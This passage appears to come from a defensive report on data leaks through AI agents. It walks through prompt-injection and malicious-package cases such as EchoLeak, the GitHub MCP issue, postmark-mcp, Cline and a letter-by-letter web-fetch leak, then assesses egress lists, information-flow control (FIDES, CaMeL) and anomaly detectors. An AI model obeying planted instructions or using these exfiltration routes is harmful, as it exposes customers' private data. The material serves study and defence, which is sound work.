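Booth and colleagues ask how agents can log their actions "and intent" in a tamper-proof way, and how to bind those actions to a person's authorisation. Signed approvals and delegation tokens partly answer the second question. Recording intent is much harder. If an agent's log contains the sentence "The customer asked for a copy of their record," a hash chain can show that the model produced it at 14:02:54. But language models can write plausible explanations that leave out what influenced them, so the sentence may have little to do with why the model chose that action.

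A better test is to rerun the case in a sandbox with fake tools. If the agent sends out the record in 18 of 20 runs with the original ticket, and in none of 20 runs without the suspicious paragraph, that paragraph very likely caused the leak. The test requires the exact input and the same model version, which the provider may have retired by then.

### The cost of keeping the records

The text needed for that test is also the most dangerous to store. A log of full prompts would put complaints, addresses and customer records from all 400 daily tickets in one place, and often more engineers can open the log than the customer database. The log would also contain the planted instruction, which could redirect any AI tool the security team uses to read logs.

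OpenTelemetry describes three ways to handle prompts and outputs: leave them out (the default), record them in the spans, or store them separately with only a reference in the span. It recommends separate storage for production systems with sensitive data or large volumes, because the separate store can have stricter access rules. This seems right for the support agent too. The default protects privacy well, but the team would be unable to tell what input caused the leak.

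Volume is also a reason to keep less telemetry. CNCF's *Filtering and reducing AI agent telemetry with the OpenTelemetry Collector* (2026) describes a coding agent's output as a wall of text that is expensive to store and hard to understand. Many tracing systems keep only a random sample of traces. If they keep 1%, there is a 99% chance that the trace for ticket 9107 is gone. Tool-call records are small enough to keep in full. At one kilobyte each, the support agent's records would take up 730 megabytes a year. If each ticket needs six model calls with 40 kilobytes of text each, the prompts add about 35 gigabytes a year, so it makes more sense to trim the prompts.

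Privacy law limits how long the company may keep these records. The European Union's General Data Protection Regulation bars organisations from keeping personal data longer than its purpose requires, and in many cases lets people have their data erased. Investigators want records kept longer, because a leak may come to light months later. A reasonable compromise is to delete prompts after perhaps 90 days and keep the tool-call records for a year or more. If Pat complained six months after the leak, the company could still identify the agent, the ticket number and the recipient, but it might have lost the text that redirected the agent.

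Erasure also conflicts with a hash chain, because deleting a record breaks the chain. The company can encrypt each customer's data with a separate key and put only the encrypted version in the chain. Destroying Pat's key then makes Pat's data unreadable while every hash still matches. An ordinary hash hides the email addresses in tool arguments poorly, because anyone with a list of customers can hash each address and compare. The company should use a keyed hash instead and store the key elsewhere.

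### Testing whether the chain holds

A company can test its attribution by having an auditor pick 60 random queries from the database's log and try to trace each one to an agent, a ticket and a responsible person. The auditor has to start at the database, because a sample from the agent's log would leave out the calls that nobody can attribute. If the auditor can trace all 60, the company can be about 95% confident that fewer than 5% of queries are untraceable, though 5% of the support agent's lookups would still be 20 a day.

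## How does data leave through an agent, and what closes each route?

Pat's record left the company in an ordinary email. The support agent could open any customer's record, had read a stranger's ticket, and could email any address. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, described this combination as access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. An attacker can easily trick an agent that has all three into fetching private data and sending it out.

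### Why removing one part is enough

An attacker can steal data with planted text only if the text reaches the model, the model's tools can access something worth stealing, and some channel leads back to the attacker. If the support agent answered only from public help pages, a malicious ticket could still redirect it, but the attacker would learn almost nothing. If the agent worked only on requests that staff wrote, the attacker's instruction would not reach it. Keeping outsiders' text away from the agent is harder than it sounds, because even the customer database contains names and addresses that customers entered themselves.

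Legitimate companies can also be a source of such text. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), Alibaba Cloud had used prompts that sought local data and operating instructions from AI agents as an anti-abuse measure, and said in December 2026 that it would stop sending them.

The company could also keep the first two parts and remove the exit, for example by having the agent draft replies for staff to send. Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, a running collection of cases and comments, describes the exit as generally the easiest part to remove. OpenAI took this approach in June 2026 with Lockdown Mode, which limits ChatGPT's outbound network requests. A planted instruction can still make ChatGPT's answer wrong, but it has far fewer ways to send data out.

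Every route by which data can leave has to be closed, including those that don't appear to send anything outside. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without approval, and those messages could contain images from outside addresses. Opening a message made a request that could carry data to an attacker. The support company's draft window has the same vulnerability if it loads outside images.

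A malicious tool is a separate problem because its code already runs where the data passes, so it can take the data without tricking the model.

### Four documented cases

In 2025, the company Aim Security found EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a company's mail and files. The attacker only had to send an email. Copilot would then produce an image whose web address contained sensitive data, and loading the image sent the data out without a click, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. The browser accepted images only from approved domains, so the researchers looked for a way out through two of them, SharePoint and Microsoft Teams. The underlying cause was that Copilot processed a stranger's email together with internal documents. Microsoft fixed its hosted service and reported no known exploitation against customers, according to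 *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2025-32711, at 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5.

In the GitHub case, the instruction arrived in a public issue, which anyone can file. A developer's agent that read the issue could open their private repositories and copy the contents into a public pull request. Willison points out that a single MCP server supplied all three parts. The cause was the blanket access that the NSA criticised rather than a single bug, so the practical fix is a token that covers only the repository the agent is working on.

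The postmark-mcp package leaked emails without any planted text. It offered an MCP server for Postmark, an email delivery service. The security company Koi reported in September 2025 that fifteen versions had worked as advertised before version 1.0.16 added a line that sent a hidden copy of every email to an address the package's developer controlled. Users were exposed because they trusted an unofficial package and its updates. The developer deleted the package from the npm registry, but installed copies remained, so users had to uninstall it and change any passwords they had sent by email.

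The strongest case of 2026 is probably the attack on Cline, an AI coding tool, because it did real damage, unlike a researcher's demonstration. According to AgentWiki's *lethal trifecta*, an attacker put instructions in the title of a GitHub issue, and an AI bot that sorted Cline's incoming issues followed them. The attacker then reached the credentials for publishing Cline's package and released a malicious version. The bot read text from strangers and could run commands in a system that gave access to those credentials. Keeping the credentials out of that system would have closed the route.

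### How the usual controls do against them

| Control | EchoLeak | GitHub server | postmark-mcp | Cline |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| List of permitted destinations | Fails; the list included possible exits | No help; GitHub itself is the exit | Helps only if the mail service checks every recipient | Might keep a stolen key from leaving |
| Content inspection | Weak against encoded data | Weak; private code looks like other code | No help; the emails themselves are normal | Might catch a key in its original form |
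| Separate tools for reading and sending | Stops it | Stops it | No help | Stops it |
| Fixed tool versions | No help | No help | Stops it for users who fixed an earlier version | Protects Cline's users, not Cline |
| Approval before sending | No help; the image loads by itself | Helps if the reviewer reads the content | No help; the server adds the copy afterwards | Helps if the reviewer recognises the command |

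These entries are judgements from the published accounts, since nobody has rerun all four attacks against each control.

### Why a permitted destination can be an exit

Egress control usually means a list of domains that software may contact. The list stops an agent from sending data directly to an attacker's own server, but a domain name doesn't identify who receives the data.

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's general-purpose agent, by default allowed outbound traffic only to certain domains, including the one for Anthropic's own API. Willison reports that in January 2026 the company PromptArmor built an attack in which the agent uploaded the user's files to that API with the attacker's key, which put them in the attacker's account. A proxy could prevent this by accepting only the key of the user's organization for that API. The NSA recommends a filtering proxy that permits only specific addresses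 and access methods. This is stricter than a list of domains, but it wouldn't block an attacker's key at a permitted address.

Lists of permitted sites also go out of date. Salesforce's Agentforce allowed images only from listed domains, but one of those domains had expired. Researchers registered it and received data about sales leads. Salesforce corrected the list and stopped the agent from producing links to untrusted addresses.

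A short list of allowed domains may not be possible for an agent that searches the web. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) calls domain lists impractical for general retrieval tools, which have to reach many sources. The support agent is easier to restrict, because ordinary code can set the recipient of each reply to the ticket's verified sender. This rule prevents mail to third parties, but if the attacker opened the ticket, the attacker is the permitted recipient. Pat's record is then protected only if the company also limits whose record the agent may open.

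### What content inspection misses

Data loss prevention (DLP) tools inspect outgoing content for sensitive data. A simple one might look for three digits, a hyphen and four digits. It would find only the first of these versions of an invented phone number:

```text
As stored    555-0142
In words     five five five, oh one four two
In Base64    NTU1LTAxNDI=
```

A better tool could decode Base64, but an attacker can ask for any encoding a language model can follow. Some secrets also have no fixed form. For example, "She is three payments behind" reveals a field from a customer's record without copying any of its text. *Names Are Not Objects* (2026) tested a system that confines coding agents, and the two attacks that still succeeded sent an encoded secret to a permitted address. The paper concludes that pattern scanning catches only careless or verbatim leaks.

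An attacker can leak data through a sequence of requests without putting the data in any single request. Claude's web-fetching tool could open only addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that appeared in pages it had already fetched. In July 2026 Ayush Paul showed how to exploit links in fetched pages, using a site with one link for each letter of the alphabet. Claude spelled out the user's name, home city and employer by following these links one letter at a time. Anthropic fixed this by no longer letting the tool follow links from fetched pages.

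The inspection also has to happen where the data leaves. ShadowLeak, a 2025 demonstration against ChatGPT's Deep Research, sent data from a connected Gmail account through the provider's own service, so the victim's company could find no trace in its browser or device records. A company also can't rely on reading the agent's answers. *Silent Egress* (2026) measured leaks from network traffic and found that data can leave through tool calls while checks on the visible output find nothing.

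DLP is still useful for catching accidental leaks, such as an employee's agent pasting a password into a public issue. For the support agent, it needs some information from the ticket, because a correct reply to Dana may well include Dana's own phone number.

### Separate tools, fixed versions and human approval

Separating the tools applies Willison's condition directly. One agent reads tickets and records but has no outside connection, while another sends email but can't open records. Data can still leak if the first agent passes the second free text, which can include Pat's phone number. Limiting the handoff to the number of a standard reply and an order status lets very little data through. That limit would work for "Where is my parcel?" but badly for an unusual complaint.

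Pinning a tool means installing one exact release and checking its hash. It would have protected anyone who had pinned postmark-mcp before version 1.0.16, but a company that first installed the package a day after that version came out would have pinned the malicious release. A valid signature doesn't prove a release is safe either. The test cases in *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026) include a signed release whose only change is an update to a library it depends on, and that library contains the hidden function. Pinning therefore has to cover those libraries too, and someone has to review updates promptly because pinning also delays security fixes.

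A remote MCP server can change without the user installing anything. The NSA describes a demonstration in which a malicious server showed a harmless tool description at first and replaced it after the second use. The new description got the client to expose messages from a separate, trusted WhatsApp server. A client can store a hash of each description and ask the user for approval again when one changes, but this check can't detect new code behind an unchanged description.

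Approval before sending depends on what the reviewer sees and how carefully they look. Users often approve a whole tool, such as web search, instead of each request, and the interface may cut off a long address before the part that contains the data. Warnings about approval fatigue usually lack measurements, but Anthropic has published a study of 1,053 paid developers that replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the developers refused it, which suggests that human approval is a poor last line of defence. Claude Code's auto mode, which decides on actions without asking the user, would have blocked 89% of the commands. Anthropic sells Claude Code, so it has an interest in this comparison, and the figures don't show whether the developers were tired or had never read the prompts closely.

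In a separate evaluation, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But the attempts covered only 72 scenarios, and zero successes in 72 independent trials would still be consistent with a true success rate of about 4%. Willison wants more independent confirmation and doubts that auto mode could stop a malicious package whose instructions look like a normal part of running the tests.

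### Information-flow control

Information-flow control attaches labels to data, copies them to everything derived from that data, and checks them before a tool call. Ordinary software does the tracking, so a planted instruction can't override its decisions.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two labels. The integrity label is either trusted or untrusted. The confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the data. When software combines two pieces of data, `x` and `y`, into `z`, the labels combine like this:

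```text
integrity(z) = trusted only if x and y are both trusted
readers(z)   = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
```

The labels form a lattice, so any two labels have a join, which is the least restrictive label that keeps the restrictions of both. Nobody can reliably tell which parts of its input a language model used, so by default the model's output takes the join of the labels on all of its input.

Before a call, the software applies one or both of these rules:

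```text
Trusted action   allow if only trusted data influenced the call
Permitted flow   allow if recipients ⊆ readers(data being sent)
```

The first rule alone lets data go to someone outside its set of readers, but only when a trusted request led to that. The second rule alone limits where the data can go, but doesn't stop an attacker from redirecting the agent. Applying both gives the strongest protection.

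### The support agent with labels

Suppose Dana writes in about a late parcel in ticket 8841. The company labels its data as follows.

| Data | Integrity | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| The company's instructions to the agent | Trusted | Anyone |
| The verified address of the sender | Trusted | Dana, staff |
| The text of the ticket | Untrusted | Dana, staff |
| Dana's record | Untrusted | Dana, staff |
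| Pat's record | Untrusted | Pat, staff |

The records count as untrusted because customers wrote parts of them. If the agent read the ticket directly, everything it did next would also be untrusted, and the trusted-action rule would block every reply, making the agent safe but useless.

FIDES, the system Costa and colleagues built, avoids this by hiding untrusted data from the model that plans. The planner sees only a variable name. A second, quarantined model can read the contents but has no tools. This arrangement, which Willison proposed in 2023, is known as the dual-LLM pattern. For Dana's ticket it would run roughly like this:

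1. Ordinary code gives the planner a trusted task, which is to answer ticket 8841.
2. The planner opens the ticket and gets back the name `#ticket`, without the text.
3. The planner asks the quarantined model to sort `#ticket` into one of four categories. The answer, "delivery", carries at most two bits, too little for an instruction, so the company's policy lets the planner use it.
4. The planner looks up the verified sender and stores the result as `#record`.
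5. The quarantined model writes a reply from `#ticket` and `#record`. The software labels `#reply` untrusted, with Dana and staff as readers.
6. The planner calls `send_email` with the verified address and `#reply`. Here the rule requires the choice of tool and the recipient to be trusted, but lets the body be untrusted. Dana is among the readers, so the email goes out.

An instruction in the ticket to fetch Pat's record never reaches the planner. If a programming mistake mixed Pat's record into the reply anyway, the readers would shrink to the people on both lists:

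`{Dana, staff} ∩ {Pat, staff} = {staff}`

Dana isn't in that set, so the software refuses the email. Paraphrasing the record or encoding it in Base64 makes no difference, because the label depends on where the data came from.

### What CaMeL and FIDES achieved

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), uses the same two kinds of model but restricts its planner more. The planner writes a short Python program from the user's request before any outside data arrives, and an interpreter runs it. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that the interpreter records each value's sources and permitted readers and checks them at every tool call. Untrusted data can determine which branch of the program runs, but it can't add a new step. FIDES lets its planner look inside a variable partway through, but then treats everything afterwards as untrusted.

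Debenedetti and colleagues reported that CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. Two injections succeeded, but neither was a clear failure of the method. In one, the user had told the agent to make whatever payment was written in a document. In the other, the benchmark counted a quoted hotel review as an attack.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on the same benchmark with GPT-4o. By their manual count, 152 injections succeeded against a basic agent without checks, 21 against FIDES without its checks, and none against any agent with checks.

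| Share of tasks completed, no attack | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 84.3% |
| Basic agent with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 41.9% |
| FIDES with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 50.0% |

The paper's headline result is that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic agent with the same checks. Its completion rate is about 34 points lower than that of an agent with no checks. A stronger model recovers some of that loss. With OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, up from 41%.

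### Follow-up work and criticism in 2026

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks. It completed about 67% to 71% of tasks with its policy checks off, depending on the model, and 37.5% with them on. With the checks on, it blocked every attack in the runs that finished. The 37.5% is hard to compare with the 77% because there are only 16 banking tasks, and many tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which these systems are designed to prevent.

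Their more serious criticism concerns the tracking itself. CaMeL marks a variable as secret when a secret affects what the program writes to it. A program can also leak a secret through something it doesn't do:

```text
a = True
b = True
if pat.in_debt: a = False
if a: b = False
if b: send_email(...)
```

If Pat is in debt, `a` becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The program then skips `b = False`, so `b` stays true and is never marked. The email goes out, and the recipient can infer from its arrival that Pat is in debt. The email leaks only one bit, but CaMeL reruns failed programs in a loop that it doesn't track, and Garby and colleagues argue that an attacker could use the loop to extract a whole secret bit by bit. Their own system also tracks the loop, and they proved its guarantee in the proof checker Lean. It completed 65% to 75% of the banking tasks when it wasn't under attack,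 and attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to follow payment instructions in a file that the attacker had replaced.

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, found that CaMeL's guarantee breaks when one protected agent calls another. The first agent treats a database entry as untrusted but includes it in a written request to the second. The second agent then treats the whole request as its user's instruction. If the support agent passed a ticket summary to a refund agent, a planted instruction could get through the same way. Their remedy is to send instructions and data in separate fields and have the interpreter keep outside data out of the instruction field. Across five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and none with the separate fields.

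Labels can also get lost when an agent runs commands. It might read a password, pack it into an archive and upload the archive to a permitted host, with each step passing its own check. *Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* (2026) therefore tracks labels in the operating system. Any program that reads a sensitive file, or a file made from one, can then send data only to destinations that follow from the user's request.

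In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) defend the approach against the criticism that its drawbacks are too great. They argue that the usual comparison is unfair because real agents ask a person before any consequential action, while the undefended agent in a benchmark acts freely. They therefore counted how many approvals each agent needed. With the model o3-mini, a basic agent needed about 48 across the tasks it completed, and FIDES needed about 19. Their own planner, Prudentia, receives the rules in advance and plans to comply with them. It completed 59.1% of tasks without any approval, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 24.3% for the basic agent. It can also ask a person to vouch for a document once, so a to-do list with ten items needs one approval instead of ten.

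This is a good argument for a company that would otherwise review everything. But Kolluri and colleagues assume the reviewer stops every malicious call, and the 13.6% refusal rate suggests many reviewers wouldn't. Vouching for a whole document also makes more depend on a single decision.

### Is the guarantee worth the lost usefulness?

The guarantee is narrower than "no data leaves". FIDES and CaMeL both assume that the tools are trustworthy, so neither would have stopped postmark-mcp, which copied emails after any check on the agent's call. The labels must also be correct. If the database returned Pat's record with "anyone" as its readers, the software would let it go to anyone. FIDES doesn't address leaks through the order or timing of calls. A permitted email can also contain false information, so the fake bank details from the earlier scam example could reach Dana in a reply that passes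 both rules.

As models have improved, it has become less obvious that CaMeL's protection is worth the loss in task completion. In the tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues, nearly all the successful attacks were on GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. Without CaMeL, attacks succeeded in 1.5% of runs with Claude Fable 5 and in none with GPT-5.5. On a separate benchmark of industrial tasks, CaMeL lowered the two strongest models' completion rate by an average of 13.4 percentage points.

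Those attacks were fixed in advance, but a real attacker can keep trying. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that in larger tests, adaptive attackers have broken every leading model. Tickets are free to open, so even a success rate of one in a thousand would eventually give an attacker a customer's record. A rule that doesn't depend on the model's judgement is valuable where a single success could expose the whole database.

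How much usefulness an agent loses also depends heavily on its job. On a benchmark of simple website tasks, where the agent never had to read untrusted text to decide what to do, Prudentia blocked every attack, needed no approvals and completed at least as many tasks as the basic agent. Most support tickets are nearly that simple, so the company could handle delivery questions and address checks this way and send unusual tickets to staff. A general office assistant would lose much more usefulness because it has to act on whatever its user's email contains.

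## Can unusual transfers be blocked automatically without stopping legitimate work?

Information-flow labels stop a transfer only where someone has labelled the data and written a rule. Anomaly detection needs no labels, because it compares an agent's current behaviour with its usual behaviour. A detector can also block a transfer without waiting for a person. Whether it should do so depends mostly on how rare theft is and how much harm a wrong block does.

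### From a call to a block

A detector starts by turning traffic into features, which are numbers it can compare over time. Suppose a malicious ticket gets the support agent to look up 50 strangers as well as the customer who wrote in. The detector might have these figures for that hour:

| Feature | Usual hour | This hour |
|---|---|---|
| Customer records returned | 50, give or take 10 | 100 |
| Data sent by email | 200 KB, give or take 50 | 210 KB |
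| Recipients not seen before | 12, give or take 4 | 13 |
| Longest run of lookups in a row | 1 to 3 | 51 |

The middle column is the baseline, which the detector learned from earlier weeks. The detector then calculates a score, for example by dividing the difference from the baseline by the usual spread:

`score = (100 − 50) ÷ 10 = 5`

With a threshold of 4, this score triggers an action, such as refusing further lookups for the ticket.

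A daily count would still miss this theft. If the standard deviation of the daily count is 50 lookups, the 50 extra lookups add only one standard deviation, and about one harmless day in six is at least that far above average. Counting over a shorter window makes the theft easier to detect, but the agent could finish 50 lookups in under a minute, so a detector has to update its counts at every call to block the theft in time.

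The most useful feature for detecting unusual transfers depends on the system. A new destination would be alarming for a database server that normally answers only the gateway, but new recipients are a weak signal for the support agent because new customers write in every day. Data volume hardly helps with the support agent either, since 50 text records fit in a short email. The order of calls works best because the agent rarely makes more than three lookups in a row.

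Several weak signals can add up to a strong one. Canale (2026), in *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response*, tested this in a simulated company modelled on Google's published infrastructure. Each signal about an account raises that account's risk:

`new risk = 1 − (1 − old risk) × (1 − signal's weight)`

Three signals with weights of 0.5, 0.3 and 0.3 raise the risk from zero to 0.5, then 0.65, then about 0.76, which is above the alert threshold of 0.7. A signal counts for less if its rule fires often. A signal with a raw score of 0.6 has a weight of 0.55 if its rule fires once a day, but 0.12 if it fires forty times a day.

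Behaviour baselines alone produced 317 false positives a day in Canale's tests. With false positives limited to ten a day, baselines detected 7% of attacks, while weighting signals by rarity detected 49%. The best version, which also used tuned rules and spread risk between linked accounts, detected 71%.

### What is normal for an agent that changes?

A baseline is only reliable if next week's traffic resembles last week's. Suppose the support company switches to a new model that does more checking and makes seven tool calls per ticket instead of five. The daily total rises from 2,000 to 2,800, and a detector that counts calls raises an alarm although nothing is wrong. The number of customers looked up per ticket stays near one, because it depends on the work rather than the model. Measures tied to the job therefore give a steadier baseline than those that vary with how the agent does it.

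In Canale's simulation, no detector caught bulk theft that appeared in only one log while staying within the alert budget. Adding a separate baseline for each account, table and hour of the day caught 29 of 39 such thefts without adding false alarms. Baselines that ignored the hour flagged nightly backups and missed most of the sudden jumps in data copied between sites. Canale added the hourly baseline after this gap appeared, so it may do less well against thefts it wasn't designed to catch.

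Detectors can flag many more harmless sessions when agents use new tools. Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, trained detectors on agents' tool calls and then hid the tools' names to simulate every tool being new. The share of harmless sessions flagged rose from 19.2% to 65.7% for one detector and from 4.5% to 73.7% for a second, which read the order of calls. Hiding some tool names at random during training kept the second detector's rate at 7% or below.

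A company can also reset the threshold after a change, but this only partly solves the problem. When Abbasi and colleagues moved their detectors to a new kind of work, they reset the thresholds using 200 unlabelled sessions. The first detector still flagged 22% to 31% of harmless sessions, and the detector that used call order found only 12% to 27% of attacks. It seems better to replay old tickets through a new version of the agent in a sandbox and build a new baseline before release. That isn't possible when a model provider changes the model without notice.

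### Why most alarms are false

Suppose a large company's agents make 1,000,000 calls a day, 10 of them malicious. A detector that catches 99% of malicious calls and wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless ones would flag about 1,000 harmless calls a day, along with about 10 malicious ones.

```text
True alarms     10 × 99%          =  9.9
False alarms    999,990 × 0.1%    ≈  1,000
Share real      9.9 ÷ 1,009.9     ≈  1%
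```

About 99 of every 100 alarms are false because harmless calls outnumber malicious ones by 100,000 to one. Catching every attack would barely change that share, because it would add only 0.1 true alarms a day. For half the alarms to be real, the false positive rate would have to fall to about 0.001%, or one harmless call in 100,000.

This is the base-rate problem, which *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 2000) applied to computer security. Axelsson imagined a small office that produced 1,000,000 log records a day and suffered two intrusions, each affecting ten records. Even a detector that missed nothing would need a false alarm rate of about one in 100,000 for two thirds of its alarms to be real. At 100 false alarms a day, about 2% of all alarms would be real, and Axelsson expected staff to stop paying attention well before that. Nobody had tested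 this on security staff, so Axelsson relied on studies of operators in places such as power stations and paper mills.

The number of false alarms also depends on whether the detector scores individual calls or whole tickets. If one in 10,000 of the support agent's tickets is malicious, the agent makes 50,000 calls for each attack, so a 0.1% false positive rate per call gives 50 false alarms. The same rate per ticket gives only 10. A whole ticket also contains more evidence than one call, so the detector may achieve a lower false positive rate. However, some data may leave before the detector has seen the whole ticket.

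### When a block pays

A low share of true alarms doesn't by itself rule out automatic blocking. Let `p` be the probability that a flagged call is theft, `C` the cost of blocking a harmless call, and `L` the loss from letting a theft through. Blocking costs `(1 − p) × C` on average, and allowing the call costs `p × L`. Blocking is cheaper when:

```text
(1 − p) × C  <  p × L
p  >  C ÷ (C + L)
```

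Suppose a missed theft costs $50,000. If a wrong block delays one customer's reply and costs $50, blocking costs less on average whenever `p`, the probability that an alarm is real, is above 0.1%. If a wrong block stops a payment run and costs $1,000, `p` has to exceed about 2%. If 1% of alarms are real, the company should block in the first case but not in the second.

Blocking prevents $495,000 in losses a day but also produces about 1,000 wrong blocks. These cost $50,000 a day at $50 each, or $1,000,000 a day at $1,000 each.

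The 1% is an average over all alarms, though, and a request for 10,000 records is more suspicious than one for six. A company could block only the transfers with the highest scores, if it has checked how often those alarms are real. The formula also holds only if blocking prevents the entire loss. If half the data has already gone, blocking saves only $25,000, and the break-even point for the $1,000 block rises to nearly 4%.

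The loss from a theft is the hardest number to estimate. A company can measure how long a wrongly blocked customer waits, but it may never have had a theft. It can still calculate how large the loss would have to be to justify blocking. If 1% of alarms are real and a wrong block costs $1,000, blocking saves money only if a theft would cost more than $99,000. Managers may find it easier to judge whether a theft would cost that much than to estimate the exact loss.

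### What tests on agent traffic have found

The best production evidence comes from Uber. *ADR* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that covers over 7,200 computers and more than 10,000 agent sessions a day. A language model screens each session, and a second model investigates the suspicious ones. Analysts judged 34% of the alerts they reviewed to be real problems and 49% to be false. The other 17% were real but harmless, mostly work by Uber's own security testers.

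These alerts were much more accurate than the 1% in the example above, partly because the most common real problem was an employee's agent exposing a credential, which happens far more often than an attack. Reviewing alerts can't show how many attacks the system missed.

Uber blocks transfers automatically only when a prompt contains a string that looks like a credential. A small program checks each prompt before the agent sends it to the model. Of the 212 strings it flagged, 206 were real credentials. Li and colleagues added this check because analysts couldn't keep up with the credential alerts, and credentials had often left the company before the alerts appeared. Such a check works because many credentials have a recognisable form, which customer data often lacks.

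Researchers have mostly tested wider detectors on benchmarks. Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, trained several standard classifiers to separate attacked sessions from harmless ones, using data that included RAS-Eval, a benchmark in MCP's format. Abbasi and colleagues used AgentDrift's synthetic sessions along with recorded runs from AgentDojo. They also tested AlignmentCheck, a Meta monitor that uses a language model to check whether each action serves the user's request.

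| Test | Attacks | Attacks found | Harmless sessions flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| Li and colleagues, Uber's benchmark | Recreated from incidents and research | 67% | 0 of 260 |
| Zavrak, XGBoost on RAS-Eval | Benchmark attacks on one model | 93% | 7% |
| Zavrak, XGBoost on ATBench | Benchmark attacks of many types | 64% | 27% |
| Abbasi and colleagues, call counts and behaviour | Synthetic | 77% | 19% |
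| Abbasi and colleagues, order of calls | Synthetic | 68% | 4.5% |
| Abbasi and colleagues, AlignmentCheck with an open model | Planted text in AgentDojo | 90% | 17% |

Only the first test has a false positive rate low enough for routine use, but it covered just 260 harmless tasks. Zero false alarms in a sample that size would still be consistent with a true rate of about 1.1%, or about 115 false alarms a day at Uber's volume. Three rival detectors flagged between 11.5% and 15.4% of the same tasks.

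The usual way of reporting results hides the base-rate problem. Abbasi and colleagues reviewed eleven evaluations and found that attacks or other anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the test sessions. If half the sessions were attacks, about 80% of the alarms from their own detector, which monitors call counts and behaviour, would be real. That share would fall to 7.6% if 2% of sessions were attacks, and to 0.4% if 0.1% were.

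A detector's performance depends more on what it can read than on its design. Zavrak measured AUROC, the probability that a detector scores a random attack above a random harmless session, where 0.5 is no better than guessing. A detector given only the tool's name, a hash of its arguments and the length of the response reached 0.64, while one that read the arguments and responses reached 0.975. A gateway that reads only headers therefore lacks most of the evidence. Even a detector that read the content found only 37% of attacks that changed only a tool's input.

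A detector that scores well at one company may not do so at another. Every detector that Abbasi and colleagues trained on AgentDrift performed close to chance on AgentDojo, including one that had been nearly perfect on AgentDrift. AlignmentCheck still performed well on AgentDojo, with an AUROC of 0.93, but if 2% of sessions were attacks, fewer than one in ten of its alarms would be real. The trained detectors were also easy to evade. Adding 1,200 characters of padding to the planted text cut the share of attacks that the call-count detector found from 77% to 3%.

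Zavrak and Abbasi and colleagues scored only completed sessions, so their results don't show how well these detectors would block transfers. A detector that must decide whether to let a call through has less evidence and less time.

Ordinary network monitoring may not fill the gap. In *When Agents Look Like Beacons*, Sohail (2026) sent synthetic MCP traffic past two widely used tools, one that looks for known attack patterns and another that looks for the regular connections malware makes to its controller. Neither raised a useful alert. However, the second tool also gave the malware-like control traffic a score of zero, because the one-minute tests produced too few connections for it to analyse. Its result therefore provides little evidence about whether it can detect a hijacked agent.

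### Letting a language model close alarms

A language model can dismiss many false alerts, but it also dismisses real ones. In Canale's simulation, two models closed about 90% of the false alerts they reviewed. They also closed every alert for 31% to 44% of the attacks that earlier stages had detected, so no analyst would have seen those attacks. Attackers could make this worse by writing a plausible excuse into a field they controlled, such as a claim that a team had authorised the work for an urgent fix.

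Fixed rules about which alerts the model could close made it much safer. High-risk alerts went straight to analysts, and the model could close others only with very high confidence. With Gemini 4, the full system found 61% of attacks with 5.8 false positives a day, and the model dismissed none of the 25 detected attacks that depended on its decision. In a second set of simulations, it dismissed 4 of 23.

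These results probably represent good conditions. The simulation recorded every system fully, and the tuned rules found 85% of the earlier attack types but only 22% of those Canale wrote after tuning. On real login records from Los Alamos National Laboratory, the detectors found a test intrusion within the alert budget only once.

### Leaks that are too slow or too fast

Suppose the company raises an alarm when any account reads more than 5,000 customer records in a day. An attacker who takes 400 extra records a day through the support agent never comes close to that limit, but has 50,000 records after 125 days.

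A running total of the excess finds this leak much sooner. The agent normally reads 400 records a day, so the company could allow 500 and carry any excess forward:

`excess today = max(0, excess yesterday + records today − 500)`

On ordinary days the total stays at zero. With the leak, the agent reads 800 records a day, and the total grows by 300. An alarm set at 1,500 goes off on the fifth day, after 2,000 records have been stolen. An attacker who takes fewer than 100 a day would still avoid detection, but would need more than 500 days to get 50,000. Counting only records unconnected to an open ticket would work better, because the usual number is close to zero.

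An attacker might also teach a self-learning detector to accept malicious activity as normal, as Axelsson warned. If the detector's baseline updates every week and the attacker raises the agent's reads by 5% each week, the reads double in about 15 weeks without a sudden jump. A fixed ceiling on reads limits this growth if only a person can raise it.

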